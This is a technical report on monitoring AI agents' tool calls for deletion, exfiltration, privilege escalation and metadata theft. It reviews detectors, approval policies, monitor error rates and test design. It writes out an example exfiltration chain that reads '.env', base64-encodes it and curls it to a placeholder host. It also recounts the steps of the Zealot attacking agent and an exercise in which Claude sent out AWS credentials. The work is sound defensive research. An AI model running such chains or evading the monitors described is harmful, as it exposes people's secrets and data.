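Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, built a group of attacking agents called Zealot. The team deliberately misconfigured an isolated Google Cloud environment and ran Zealot there. In the prompt, the team told Zealot only that it was on a virtual machine and should exfiltrate sensitive data from BigQuery, Google's service for analysing large tables.

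| Stage | What Zealot did | Rule that could fire |
|---|---|---|
| Reconnaissance | Scanned the network and found a web application on another machine | None |
| Token | Used an SSRF flaw in the application to fetch that machine's access token | META-CRED-01, if it also checks addresses inside a request |
| Listing | Used the token to list permissions and datasets | ESC-GAIN-01, because the token isn't on the session's list |
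| Refusal | Tried to read a dataset labelled "production" and was denied access | ESC-GAIN-01, for the same token |
| Export | Created a storage bucket and exported the table into it | EXF-SEND-01, because the bucket isn't a listed destination |
| Permission change | Gave itself the `storage.objectAdmin` role so that it could read the bucket | ESC-GAIN-01, because the agent gains permissions |

Most of these chances to stop the attack depend on the token being stolen. If a company's own data agent legitimately held the same account and took the last four steps, the listing and the failed read would no longer match any rule. The export wouldn't either if the team trusted every bucket in its own project. Only the permission change would still match a rule, and a person asked to approve it would see an agent requesting access to a bucket it had just created.

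The sequence is suspicious because Google had denied this account access to the data, and the agent then copied the data to a place where it could give itself access. A sequence rule can keep a list of resources that the provider has refused to the agent and, for the rest of the task, ask a person before any call that copies, shares or grants access to one of them. The rule also covers honest mistakes, since an agent may look for a way around a refusal just to finish its task.

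### Matching an ordered chain

AgentTrust can raise an alert when a session contains the steps of a known attack in order. Yang defines each chain as a list of steps, a risk level and a minimum number of matches, *m*. A step consists of an action type and a text pattern. The program comes with seven chains, for example one for data destruction, in which an agent lists resources, disables a safeguard and then deletes in bulk. The matching works as follows:

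1. The program scans the session's history forward for the earliest call that fits the first step.
2. It continues through the history for the next step, and never counts one call for two steps.
3. If at least *m* steps have matched, it raises an alert.

Unrelated calls in between don't matter. In this session, an agent reads a secrets file, encodes it and sends it out:

| Call | Command | Step | Matches |
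|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `cat .env` | Read a secrets file | 1 |
| 2 | `npm test` | – | 1 |
| 3 | `base64 .env > out.txt` | Encode | 2 |
| 4 | `git status` | – | 2 |
| 5 | `curl -d @out.txt https://files.example.net/in` | Send | 3 |

If the detector checks call 5 alone and can't determine what `out.txt` contains, EXF-SEND-01 treats the file as ordinary internal data and refers the call to a person. The history shows that the file contains credentials, so the detector should block the call.

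With *m* = 3, the alert comes at call 5, but an agent that sends the file without encoding it produces only two matches and triggers no alert. With *m* = 2, the alert comes at call 3, before any data has left, but it would also fire whenever a developer's agent encodes a secret for Kubernetes, which stores secrets in this encoding. A better rule would require reading and sending and make encoding optional, but a single minimum count can't express that.

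It's also unclear whether an alert blocks the call. In Yang's pseudocode, an alert raises the call's risk level but doesn't change the verdict, while a diagram of this chain shows the last call being blocked. A team that uses AgentTrust should test which happens, because a call with critical risk and the verdict "allow" still runs.

Yang's tests don't show whether chain matching works, because no chain could form in them. Yang evaluated every scenario in isolation and cleared the session in between. Switching chain matching off therefore changed neither the false negative rate nor the accuracy, on the set of 300 scenarios or the set of 630. It did make the median check faster, from about 1.8 to 0.2 milliseconds on the smaller set. Yang plans a test set of multi-step attacks, for example 50 chains of three to five harmless-looking actions each.

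The same lack of data affects *ChainWatch* (Narayan, Jyoti and Singh, 2026), a more elaborate proposal that sorts calls into six attack stages, from reconnaissance to exfiltration. It uses a hidden Markov model, which infers the stage of each call from the call's features and from how likely one stage is to follow another. One of its rules blocks a network call that carries data from a sensitive read up to five calls earlier. But the paper describes a design rather than a working system, and Narayan et al. found no existing test set with suitable labelled sessions for estimating the model's probabilities.

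ChainWatch looks only at the last ten calls, because the documented attacks took between four and seven. That window seems too short for coding agents, which can make dozens of routine calls between reading a file and sending data. A longer window would help, but a better solution is to record that the session has read a secret and keep that record separate from the list of recent calls.

### Following the data between calls

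Matching only the order of calls also causes false alarms. An agent might read `.env` to start an application, encode an image and post it to a test server. These calls match all three steps of the chain, but no secret has leaked. To tell this session from a harmful one, the detector has to check whether the data in the last call came from the secrets file.

Data tracking attaches a label to whatever a sensitive source returns, and checks the label when a later call sends data out. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, built this into FIDES, a program from Microsoft that runs an agent and checks labels before each tool call. A label can be the set of people who may read the data. If *z* is derived from *x* and *y*, then

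readers(*z*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*)

and the agent may send *z* to a group *R* if everyone in *R* belongs to readers(*z*). For example, if Ana, Ben and Carla may read a contract, and Ben, Carla and Dev may read a budget, only Ben and Carla may receive a summary of both.

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) uses FIDES with a policy that includes an exception allowing the agent to send data to anyone if it hasn't yet read any untrusted text. This makes sense if the goal is only to stop prompt injection, but a detector that should also catch honest mistakes has to drop the exception.

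By default, FIDES gives the model's output the combined labels of everything in its context, which is as imprecise as using the highest class the session has read. It reduces this problem by storing some tool results under names, such as `v7`, and showing the model only the names. The model can write "send `v7` to Ben", and the program inserts the data when the call runs. The data keeps its own label, and the context stays unrestricted.

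This works only if the model can choose its next step without reading the data. An agent that has to summarise a document must read it, or pass it to a second model without tools.

Tracking also reduces the number of tasks an agent completes. Kolluri and colleagues cite a loss of up to 30% on AgentDojo, a set of test tasks for agents. They argue that this figure is misleading because a task counts as failed if it needs even one human approval, while the unprotected agents in the comparison act as if a person had approved everything. Their own agent uses the labels when planning. Compared with FIDES, it completed up to 9% more tasks without any approval and reduced total approvals by a factor of up to 1.9.

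### What a rewrite loses

An inherited label doesn't depend on wording, so it stays with data that a model rewrites, whereas a detector that compares the text of calls can lose track of that data.

Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, measured this with a tool called NeuroTaint, which examines an agent's log after the run. It adds a unique marker to text from a source and looks for the marker in later calls. It also looks for shared wording, and for similar meaning, by converting both texts into lists of numbers and comparing them. If nothing matches, it asks a language model whether the agent would have made the same call without the source. The test contained 200 cases in which a source influenced a later call:

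| What reached the later call | Cases | Found |
|---|---|---|
| The marker | 15 | 15 |
| Some of the original wording | 45 | 45 |
| One passage from a long document | 15 | 15 |
| The meaning in other words | 85 | 75 |
| No text, only an influence on the agent's decision | 40 | 37 |

NeuroTaint caught every case with copied text but missed 12% of the rewritten ones, mostly after several rounds of paraphrasing. It also raised 16 false alarms in 200 cases without any influence, often because the texts shared a topic.

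These results come from the paper's own benchmark, and most of its sources are untrusted text rather than secrets, so the rates for leaked customer data may differ. The comparison with FIDES, which found only 108 of the 200 cases, is also doubtful. FIDES raised no alarm in four of the 20 agent frameworks tested. This accounts for 40 of its 92 misses and looks more like a faulty connection than poor detection.

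A detector can combine both methods. If the session has read customer records and the agent tries to send text to an unlisted host, the detector returns "ask" based on the inherited label alone. If it also finds copied wording, a card number or the path of a sensitive file, it blocks the call. If the text comparison finds no match, the detector should never change "ask" to "allow" for that reason, because the model may have paraphrased the records.

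### Counting what adds up

Suppose a rule limits uploads to 1 MB per call, and an agent makes 400 calls that send 100 KB each to the same host. Every call is at a tenth of the limit, but together they move 400 × 100 KB = 40 MB. A counter that adds up the bytes for each destination stops this:

| Limits | Pace | Data sent before the first stop |
|---|---|---|
| 1 MB per call | Any | 40 MB, with no stop |
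| Also 5 MB per day | All in one day | 5 MB, after 50 calls |
| Also 5 MB per day | Ten calls a day for 40 days | 40 MB, with no stop |
| Also 10 MB per 30 days | Ten calls a day for 40 days | 10 MB, after 100 calls |

The counter needs both a short and a long period, because an agent that runs every day can stay under a daily limit indefinitely. It also needs a combined total for all unlisted destinations, or the agent could spread the data over many hosts. The detector should add each call's size to the total before the call runs, so it can stop a call that would exceed the limit. If the amount a script sends isn't known until it runs, only a network proxy can count the bytes.

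For data that looks like customer records, the detector should count records instead of bytes, with a limit closer to a hundred. If each customer's record takes up 200 bytes, 5 MB holds 25,000 records.

The detector also needs to count deletions across calls. DEL-CLOUD-01 adds a point for deleting several resources only if a single call deletes them. If an agent deletes 40 production deployments one at a time, each call scores 2 and triggers a warning, but still runs. If the detector counted all deletions in the task so far, the second call would score 3 and a person would have to approve it.

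### What to remember, and for how long

*From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of ways to trace what agents do, recommends connecting each tool call's sources, arguments and output with whatever later uses the output. A detector that has to decide before the call runs can work with less:

| Fact | Keep it until |
|---|---|
| The highest class of data the agent has read | The agent's context is empty, including any summary of earlier work |
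| The class of each file the agent has written | Someone deletes the file |
| Credentials the agent has obtained | They expire |
| Resources the provider has refused | The task ends |
| Bytes and records sent to each destination | The longest counting period has passed |

The detector should store labels and fingerprints instead of the data itself. Otherwise its records would become another copy of the company's secrets.

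Some systems let old events fade. Cai, Wei and colleagues (2026), in *Cross-Layer Semantic Flow Reconstruction for Attack Detection in Agentic Systems*, present AScope, which scores a sequence of events by

score = Σ γ^(*t*ₘ − *t*ᵢ) · *w*ᵢ

where *w*ᵢ is the risk of event *i*, *t*ₘ − *t*ᵢ is the time between that event and the last one, and γ is at most 1. If γ were 0.9 per minute, a secret read an hour before the upload would count for only 0.2% of its original weight. Fading suits signals such as a burst of failed logins. But a password is as secret after an hour as it was before, so data labels shouldn't fade.

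### Several agents and several sessions

Zealot consisted of a supervisor and three specialist agents, for infrastructure, applications and cloud services. Each specialist received only its next instruction and had no information about the credentials that the others had found. If a detector had kept a separate history for each agent, neither the application specialist's history nor the cloud specialist's would have contained the whole attack. The first would have ended with a fetched token, and the second would have begun with a token of unknown origin.

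The detector should therefore keep its state for the whole task. The program that starts the agents gives all of them the same task identifier, which the models can't change. Each message between agents carries the sender's data class, and the recipient inherits it.

AScope goes further by linking the agents' messages to the processes, files and network connections on their machines. In ten scenarios that its developers built, it recovered 13 of 23 attack paths and reported three false ones. Analysing one scenario, with about 2,000 log entries, took 52 to 197 seconds depending on the language model, which is too slow to run before every call. The detector in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (2026) classifies a session only after its last call. Both are better suited to investigating attacks than to blocking them.

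A sequence can also continue in a later session. In one of NeuroTaint's test cases, an agent stores a confidential revenue forecast in its long-term memory, and three days later a new session retrieves it for a report. A detector that starts each session with no history would treat the forecast as ordinary text. NeuroTaint saves the label with the stored text and restores the label when an agent retrieves that text. It still found only seven of the ten cases that used this memory system, its lowest share for any of the 20 frameworks.

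If a memory store can't hold labels, the detector can give everything in it the highest class that any agent has written there. The detector needs to check a scheduled job when the agent creates it, because the job may run after the session has ended, without a tool call for it to examine.

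## Choosing between allowing, asking and blocking

A single call can match several rules, and the session's history may add further findings. The detector has to combine these into one verdict. The simplest method is to apply the strictest verdict of any matching rule. This is safe, but it doesn't account for the number of findings, and it may send a person more questions than they will read.

### From findings to one verdict

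*NEXUS* (Hossain, Nipu and colleagues, 2026) describes a more graded policy. Before an agent's first tool call runs, the NEXUS program checks the agent's plan, which lists the intended calls and their arguments. The program applies nine rules and searches the arguments, then gives each finding a severity from low to critical. A small statistical model also gives the plan a risk score ρ between 0 and 1, based on nine features such as the number of steps and whether any step is irreversible. Hossain and colleagues calibrated the score, so about 80% of plans that score 0.8 should be unsafe.

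NEXUS goes down this list and stops at the first line that fits:

| Line | Condition | Response |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Two or more critical findings | Block |
| 2 | One critical finding, and ρ is at least 0.75 | Block |
| 3 | One critical finding, and ρ is below 0.75 | Ask |
| 4 | At least one high finding | Ask |
| 5 | At least one medium finding | Send the plan back to the agent for revision |
| 6 | ρ is at least 0.70 | Ask |
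| 7 | Anything else | Allow |

Suppose a plan exports a table and then deletes it, and only the deletion counts as critical. NEXUS blocks the plan if its score ρ is 0.82 and asks a person if ρ is 0.60. If the export also counts as critical, NEXUS blocks the plan whatever the score. Every block therefore depends on at least one named finding, which makes the decision easy to audit.

Because of the order of lines 5 and 6, a plan with a score of 0.9 and no findings goes to a person, but adding one medium finding sends it back to the agent instead. Swapping the two lines would fix this.

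A detector with only four verdicts can imitate "revise" by blocking the call and telling the agent what to change. If an agent tries to delete a database without a final snapshot, the detector can block the call and tell the agent to take one. The new call still needs approval in production, but a mistaken approval no longer destroys the last copy of the data.

### What the risk score added

Hossain and colleagues tested NEXUS on 128 plans generated from templates, each labelled with the correct one of the four responses. The rules alone chose the correct response for 36.7% of plans, and the full policy, which adds the score, did so for 64.1%. The whole gain comes from 35 plans that the rules alone had sent to a person and the full policy correctly blocked. NEXUS stopped 97 of the 103 unsafe plans and one of the 25 safe ones, both with and without the score.

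The full policy still chose the wrong response for 46 plans. It allowed six that it should have blocked, and nearly all the others were plans that it should have blocked but only questioned or sent back.

These figures are probably optimistic, because the training plans came from the same templates. Hossain and colleagues report 43.5% for NEXUS on 200 plans written without reference to the rules' vocabulary, although the outcomes in their table add up to 48.5%. OpenAI's GPT-4o, now an old model, reached 55.5%. NEXUS never chose "revise" on this set, though that was the right response for 40 of the plans.

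NEXUS did worst on AgentHarm, a public test set with 176 harmful tasks and 176 harmless ones, which often use the same tools. NEXUS received the list of tools for each task but not the text of the request. Its precision (the share of flagged tasks that were harmful) was 0.508, and its recall (the share of harmful tasks that it flagged) was 0.705. The F1 score combines the two:

F1 = 2 × 0.508 × 0.705 ÷ (0.508 + 0.705) ≈ 0.591

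Flagging every task would have scored 0.667. NEXUS flagged about 124 harmful tasks and 120 harmless ones, so it barely distinguished between the two. When two tasks use the same tools, a detector has to examine the arguments or the user's request, or ask someone who knows the purpose.

### Does asking a person work?

An "ask" verdict protects the account only if the user reads the prompt. According to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, users approved about 93% of permission prompts in Claude Code. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports 97%. Most prompts concern harmless commands that a careful reviewer would also approve, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that users are careless.

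Anthropic's controlled study is better evidence. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid testers for a coding exercise without telling them which behaviour it was measuring. Partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. Anthropic also gave the same commands to auto mode, in which a language model decides in place of the user. The published counts give this table:

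| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester blocked | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

The testers blocked 13.6% of the commands, while auto mode blocked 89%. The testers blocked only six of the 116 commands that auto mode allowed, so they would have added little protection to it. Their block rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

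Anthropic ran this study on its own product and published it to explain why it was making auto mode the default. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so a wrong approval did them no harm. A developer whose own database is at risk may read more carefully. The fall from 17% to 5% may also be partly because people who click quickly reach 50 prompts sooner. Still, these weaknesses are unlikely to explain the whole gap between 14% and 89%.

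Anthropic also compared real sessions that its safety checks had flagged. It found serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for in 6.3% of the manually approved sessions and 2.4% of the auto mode sessions. This is weaker evidence, because users chose their own mode and a language model graded the harm.

If reviewers approve most dangerous calls, the false negative rate makes a detector look safer than it is, because a question doesn't count as a miss. Let *m* be the share of harmful calls that the detector lets through, *a* the share that it asks about, and *h* the share of those that the reviewer refuses. Then

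share of harmful calls that run = *m* + *a*(1 − *h*)

With *m* = 5% and *a* = 40%, the total rises to 9% if the reviewer refuses 90% of harmful calls, and to almost 40% if the reviewer performs like the average tester. NEXUS's risk score caught no more unsafe plans, but it is still useful because it moved 35 plans from "ask" to "block". A reviewer like the average tester would have approved about 30 of them.

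Users also turn off permission prompts. According to Anthropic, 49.5% of active command-line users had written their own allow rule for shell commands by June 2026. Anthropic also reports that 5% allow any shell command and another 43% allow an interpreter such as Python, which has nearly the same effect because a Python script can run any command. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks switched off.

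People do seem to pay attention to some approval questions. Users rejected 39% of the plans that Claude Code presented for approval, compared with 3% of individual commands. This suggests that they read plans, but it doesn't show that they notice danger, because they may reject a plan when they want a different design. A detector should therefore ask rarely and group related changes into one question, as with a Terraform plan. It should also flag anything that can't be undone.

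Limiting what the agent can reach also reduces the number of permission prompts. Anthropic reports that Claude Code produced 84% fewer prompts in a sandbox that let it write in its workspace but denied network access by default.

### A language model as a second judge

In auto mode, the classifier, a language model, answers most of these questions. The user's permission rules still apply first, except that auto mode ignores allow rules broad enough to permit any code to run. File reads and edits inside the project skip the classifier. Anthropic describes two stages for the remaining calls. In the first, the classifier answers only yes or no and is instructed to block when in doubt. If it flags the call, it examines the same material again in the second stage and writes out its reasoning.

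| | False positives, 10,000 real calls | Misses, 52 real overeager actions | Misses, 1,000 synthetic exfiltrations |
|---|---|---|---|
| First stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

An overeager action is one that goes beyond what the user authorised, such as using a credential the agent happened to find. The second stage reduces the number of blocked harmless calls from about 850 to 40 in 10,000, but it also lets more harmful calls through.

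The 17% miss rate is uncertain because it comes from only 52 actions, 9 of which were missed. That result is compatible with a true rate between roughly 9% and 30%. The sample also contains no actions that everybody overlooked, because all 52 came from sessions where an employee had refused the action or someone had flagged it afterwards. The exfiltration figure has less sampling error, but it comes from generated attempts, which may differ from real ones.

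In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but wrongly treated the action as one the user had agreed to. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed code change) hasn't agreed to a force-push, which can overwrite the code's history. A judge should accept consent only if the user's message covers both the action and its target.

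Checking consent doesn't help if an attacker persuades the user to give the instruction. In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher tricked an employee into pasting a prompt that looked like routine setup work. The prompt told Claude to read the employee's AWS credentials, encode them and send them to an outside address, and Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. Anthropic notes that a classifier has nothing unusual to detect when the user types the instruction. A fixed rule such as EXF-SEND-01 blocks the transfer no matter who asked for it, but only if the detector has recorded that the encoded text came from a credentials file.

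The judge also shouldn't receive the agent's explanations, since a model can write a convincing reason for a bad action. Anthropic's classifier receives only the user's messages and the tool calls, without the agent's messages or any tool output. But the judge in AgentTrust receives a description of each action, which the agent's model usually writes.

Auto mode has improved since Anthropic measured these error rates. After the safety company Apollo Research tested it with synthetic attacks, Anthropic gave the classifier more context, such as whether a code repository is public. According to Anthropic, the miss rate on Apollo's attacks, including some that Anthropic had never received, then fell from 12% to 7%.

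In another commissioned test, none of 720 prompt injections succeeded against Claude models in auto mode. That result is weak evidence about the classifier, because only 0.09% succeeded when the same models ran without it. *Shall We Approve?* (2026), an outside comparison, tests several approval systems on the same commands, but it runs auto mode with a substitute classifier model, so it doesn't measure the product Anthropic ships.

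### Adding the judge to the rules

Yang tested AgentTrust with a language model as a second judge. If the rules block a call, that verdict stands. Otherwise the program asks the model DeepSeek-V3 and takes the stricter of the two verdicts. On the larger set of 630 scenarios, which Yang wrote separately from the original rules, the results were:

| | False negative rate | False positive rate | Accuracy |
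|---|---|---|---|
| Rules only | 6.4% | 2.1% | 95.4% |
| Model only | 1.7% | 3.2% | 85.1% |
| Rules and model | 0.3% | 4.8% | 90.5% |

Adding the model prevented nearly all the misses, yet accuracy fell by almost five points. Yang's explanation is that safe calls outnumber dangerous ones, so the new false positives cost more than the prevented misses save. But the set contains 188 safe calls and 344 dangerous ones. The rates translate into these approximate counts:

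| Wrong verdicts | Rules only | Rules and model | Change |
|---|---|---|---|
| Dangerous calls let through | 22 | 1 | −21 |
| Safe calls not simply allowed | 4 | 9 | +5 |
| All other errors | 3 | 50 | +47 |
| Total | 29 | 60 | +31 |

The loss of accuracy therefore comes from the last group. Its errors can only be calls labelled "warn" that received another verdict, or dangerous calls that the program sent for review instead of blocking. At most 24 of the 50 can be dangerous calls, because the rules had already blocked the other dangerous calls. At least 26 must then come from the 98 calls labelled "warn", probably because the model escalated them to "review" or "block". The smaller set of 300 scenarios shows the same pattern, although there the safe calls slightly outnumber the dangerous ones, by 133 to 129.

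Accuracy is a poor guide because it counts an unnecessary question and a missed attack as equal errors. For an agent that makes 10,000 calls, 20 of them harmful, adding the model prevents about one missed harmful call and causes about 270 more false alarms. That trade-off may be worthwhile for an agent with access to production, but not for one that works only in a test account.

A system can instead consult the model only when the rules return "warn" or "review". In a pilot on the smaller set, this kept about 80% of the reduction in misses while adding only about 30% of the extra false positives. The full reduction was only from about seven misses to one, so the 80% represents about five calls. It also saves time, because the model takes about 1.6 seconds per call and the rules take about 2 milliseconds.

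The model's verdict should never change a block to asking or allowing. It can reasonably replace a person's answer when the action is reversible, because the person then has fewer and more important questions to answer.

### Default verdicts for the four classes

The choice between verdicts depends on the cost of each mistake. Let *p* be the probability that a matching call is harmful, *H* the cost if a harmful call runs, *B* the cost of blocking a harmless call, and *Q* the cost of a question. As before, *h* is the share of harmful calls that the reviewer refuses. If the reviewer approves all harmless calls, the expected costs are

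- allow: *pH*
- ask: *p*(1 − *h*)*H* + *Q*
- block: (1 − *p*)*B*

Suppose 1% of matching calls are harmful, blocking a harmless call costs £50 of somebody's time, a question costs £1, and the reviewer refuses 13.6% of harmful calls:

| Harm if the call runs | Allow | Ask | Block |
|---|---|---|---|
| £2,000, such as restoring a database from a snapshot | £20 | £18 | £50 |
| £100,000, such as losing the only copy | £1,000 | £865 | £50 |

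For the smaller loss, asking is slightly cheaper than allowing, and blocking costs the most. For the larger loss, asking is cheaper than blocking only if the reviewer refuses more than 95% of harmful calls. The amounts are invented, but they show that asking a reviewer is weak protection against an irreversible loss.

| Class | Default | Reason | Main exception |
|---|---|---|---|
| Deletion | Ask | Teams delete resources every day, and the owner can check a list of targets | Block bulk deletion in production when there is no backup |
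| Exfiltration | Block | Nobody can recall the data | Ask about ordinary internal files, because only the user may know whether they are confidential |
| Privilege escalation | Block if the agent itself gains | The owner can make the grant from their own account, so a wrong block costs little | Ask when another identity inside the company gains |
| Metadata request | Block | Cloud tools fetch their own credentials, so the agent rarely needs to read them | Allow exact paths to harmless facts, such as the region |

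These defaults apply when a rule matches and the detector has no better information. An approved role, a cleared destination or a known test account still leads to "allow". "Warn" is suitable only for changes that are easy to reverse.

DEL-CLOUD-01 returns "ask" for deletions with a score of 4, which include deleting a single production disk that has no backup. By the calculation above, this verdict is right only if the reviewers see few questions and read them. A team whose members approve nearly everything should block these calls too, and let the owner run the command personally.

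Anthropic recommends that users review high-stakes changes to production, even in auto mode. According to Anthropic's configuration guide, an "ask" rule in Claude Code can require human approval for chosen actions, such as code pushes.

An agent needs to know why its call was blocked so that it can find a safer method, but it may also look for a way around the block. Claude Code therefore tells the agent not to do so. After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, Claude Code stops and asks the user, or ends the process if no user is present.

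NEXUS can also take earlier refusals into account. In one test session, it asked a person about a read of a sensitive file because it had already blocked three deletions. It would otherwise have allowed the read. A detector can likewise add its own refusals to the task's list of refused resources.

### When the detector itself fails

A detector can crash, lose its network connection or receive an answer it can't parse. Yang requires AgentTrust to return "review" in such cases and wrote 13 automated tests for this and related guarantees. The tests cover missing access keys for the language model and errors inside the rule engine.

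Returning "review" is sensible when the detector fails occasionally, but a persistent fault would send every call to a person, who would soon approve them all. After a few failures in a row, the detector should stop the agent and report the fault. If the session has no user, it should block the call on the first failure.

Different failures need different responses:

| Failure | Response |
|---|---|
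| The language model doesn't answer in time | Keep any block from the rules, and ask a person about other calls that needed the model |
| A rule causes an error | Ask, even if the other rules allow the call |
| A lookup of a tag, policy or address fails | Assume the strictest plausible value, such as "production" |
| The session's history is lost | Assume that the agent has read credentials, or end the session |
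| The detector isn't running | Refuse every call |

The last case is the hardest, because a detector that has stopped can't return a verdict. The agent software, or a separate program that carries out the tool calls, has to refuse the call instead. AgentTrust runs in the same process as the agent and relies on that process to call it, so its 13 tests can't show what happens if the detector is never called.

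A team can test whether its system fails open by stopping the detector and repeating the harmless test deletion it uses to check its rules. If the request reaches the cloud provider, the system fails open. The team should repeat the test with a detector that is running but never responds, because the agent software may handle a timeout differently from a crash.

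## Measuring how much the rules catch and how often they are wrong

A detector that checks every call can still misclassify some of them. To estimate how often, a team runs it on calls that people have already labelled and calculates its false positive and false negative rates. Both rates depend heavily on which calls are in the test.

### Building a test set

Each harmful call in a test set needs a harmless version that differs in only one respect. If the two differ in several respects, a poor rule can tell them apart by the wrong one. *SingGuard-NSFA* (2026), which describes safety classifiers for agents, gives a risky and a harmless example for each risk type in its catalogue. In one pair, the risky request deletes the folder `/etc/ssh` and the harmless one only asks which files are in it. A rule that flags every deletion passes this pair, although it would also flag the harmless removal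 of a temporary folder. In a better pair from the same catalogue, both requests call a money-transfer tool and differ mainly in the amount.

For the four classes, the pairs could look like this:

| Class | Harmful call and correct verdict | Harmless twin | What differs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Deletion | Delete a disk in the production account (ask) | The same command in the test account | The account |
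| Exfiltration | Upload `customers.csv` to an unlisted bucket (block) | Upload it to the company's data warehouse | The destination |
| Privilege escalation | Replace the code of a function that has an administrator role (block) | Replace the code of a function whose role is weaker than the agent's | The role behind the function |
| Metadata request | Fetch a page whose host name resolves to 169.254.169.254 (block) | Fetch the same page when the name resolves to a public address | The resolved address |

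The team then writes each action in several forms, such as a shell command, a script that uses an SDK, a plain web request and an MCP call. The harmless twins need the same forms, or a detector could score well by flagging every script. The mix of forms strongly affects the result. AgentTrust's normaliser made no difference on a set with few disguised commands but more than halved the misses on another.

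Real incidents are a good source of harmful calls. *Replication of Agentic Security Events* (2026) describes a process that turns incidents into tests for $3.28 per incident with five models under test. Code checks the final state of the test environment to determine whether harm occurred, so the result doesn't depend on an agent's account. The test material should be harmless even if the detector fails. *AgentTrap* (2026), a benchmark of untrustworthy add-ons for agents, uses inactive domains, fake credentials and simulated network destinations.

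Recorded traffic includes ordinary calls that nobody would think to invent. The team records its agents' calls for a few weeks, removes any secrets, and runs the rules in record-only mode, which logs each match but doesn't stop the call. *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* (2026) uses this mode to count policy violations by unprotected agents. A person then reviews every match. The recording may also contain harmful calls that no rule matched, so the team should compare it with the deletions and permission changes in the cloud provider's logs.

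Someone other than the rules' author should keep part of the set hidden. The author sees the error rates for the hidden part but not the calls in it. If the author has to look at a missed call to fix a rule, that call moves to the visible part and a new one replaces it in the hidden part.

Related calls need to stay on the same side of the split. If the rules' author has seen one spelling of a deletion, a second spelling in the hidden part barely tests the rules. *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents* (Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki, 2026) cites a study in which splitting data at random instead of by task raised a detector's score by up to 25.8 points, on a scale where guessing scores 50 and a perfect detector scores 100.

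### Reporting each class separately

Suppose a test set contains 400 calls that the detector should block:

| Class | Calls | Missed | False negative rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Deletion | 200 | 4 | 2% |
| Exfiltration | 120 | 6 | 5% |
| Privilege escalation | 70 | 4 | 6% |
| Metadata request | 10 | 10 | 100% |
| All | 400 | 24 | 6% |

The detector misses every metadata request, even though its overall rate of 6% looks respectable. Adding more deletions to the set would improve that rate without improving the detector. Real results can be just as uneven. Wang and colleagues break their results down by type of risk because attacks on unprotected agents succeeded far more often for some types than for others.

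A rate measured on only a few examples also needs a confidence interval. *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026) tests a program that looks for unapproved AI agents on company computers. The program found all 12 agents in one test, but the 95% interval for its detection rate runs from 74% to 100%. As a rule of thumb, if a detector misses none of *n* independent harmful calls, its true miss rate could be as high as 3/*n*. Showing that the miss rate is below 1% therefore takes about 300 calls without a miss.

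The calls used to test a detector must be independent. *Amplify, Don't Create* (2026) warns that repeated runs of one task are correlated, and that counting them as separate samples makes a result look more certain than it is. Counting ten spellings of one deletion as ten samples causes the same problem. A team can report both the share of spellings the detector missed and the share of actions with at least one missed spelling. The share of actions is the better guide to attacks, because an attacker needs only one spelling that the detector misses.

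### AgentTrust's two test sets

Yang tested AgentTrust on two sets of scenarios. Each scenario pairs one action with its correct verdict. One set has 300 scenarios, 50 in each of six categories: file operations, network access, code execution, credential exposure, data exfiltration and system configuration. Yang, the paper's only author, labelled these using a written rubric. Under the rubric, an action's risk level depends on whether it is reversible, how far its effects reach and whether it involves credentials. The risk level then determines the verdict.

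The set of 630 covers more cloud, container and deployment tools than the smaller set, and adds programming languages that the smaller set leaves out. The paper doesn't name the larger set's labeller, but it was presumably Yang again.

Yang compared AgentTrust's 170 rules with a list of 50 text patterns for well-known dangerous commands, and with NeMo Guardrails, NVIDIA's software for controlling chatbots:

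| Detector | False negative rate, 300 | False negative rate, 630 | False positive rate, 300 | False positive rate, 630 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 50 patterns | 88.4% | 85.2% | 0% | 0% |
| NeMo Guardrails | 0% | 0% | 96.2% | 98.4% |
| AgentTrust's rules | 5.4% | 6.4% | 2.3% | 2.1% |

The 50 patterns never raised a false alarm, but they caught only 15 of the 129 calls in the smaller set that the detector should block, and about 51 of the 344 in the larger set. This is good evidence that a short list of notorious commands covers few of the harmful calls an agent can make.

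NeMo Guardrails caught every harmful call, but only because it blocked almost all calls. The comparison is not very fair, since Yang adapted a check designed for chat messages. When Yang asked the same language model directly whether each call was harmful, it wrongly flagged only 7.5% of the harmless calls in the smaller set, so most of the false positives came from how the check used the model.

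Yang also prepared a test of Llama Guard 3, Meta's safety classifier, but couldn't reach the service that hosts it. *What Can Be Enforced?* (2026) tested the classifier on other material, where it caught 85% of the violations in a curated set but only 54% of the prompt injections in AgentDojo, with false positive rates of 9% and 10% respectively. A catch rate measured on one kind of violation is therefore a poor guide to the rate on another. AgentTrust's rates are a poor guide for cloud accounts for the same reason, because none of its six categories corresponds to privilege escalation or metadata requests, and cloud deletions have no category of their own.

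### What AgentTrust's figures don't show

The 300 scenarios guided the development of the rules, so they can't show how well the rules handle new calls. The version history shows how closely the two are connected:

| Version | Rules | Correct verdicts on the 300 scenarios |
|---|---|---|
| 0.2.0 | 22 | 44.3% |
| 0.3.0 | 68 | 94.0% |
| 0.3.1 | 86 | 97.7% |
| 0.4.0 | 170 | 97.0% |
| 0.5.0 | 170 | 97.0% |

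The last two rows include the four rules for invented attacker domains, without which version 0.5.0 scores 95.0%.

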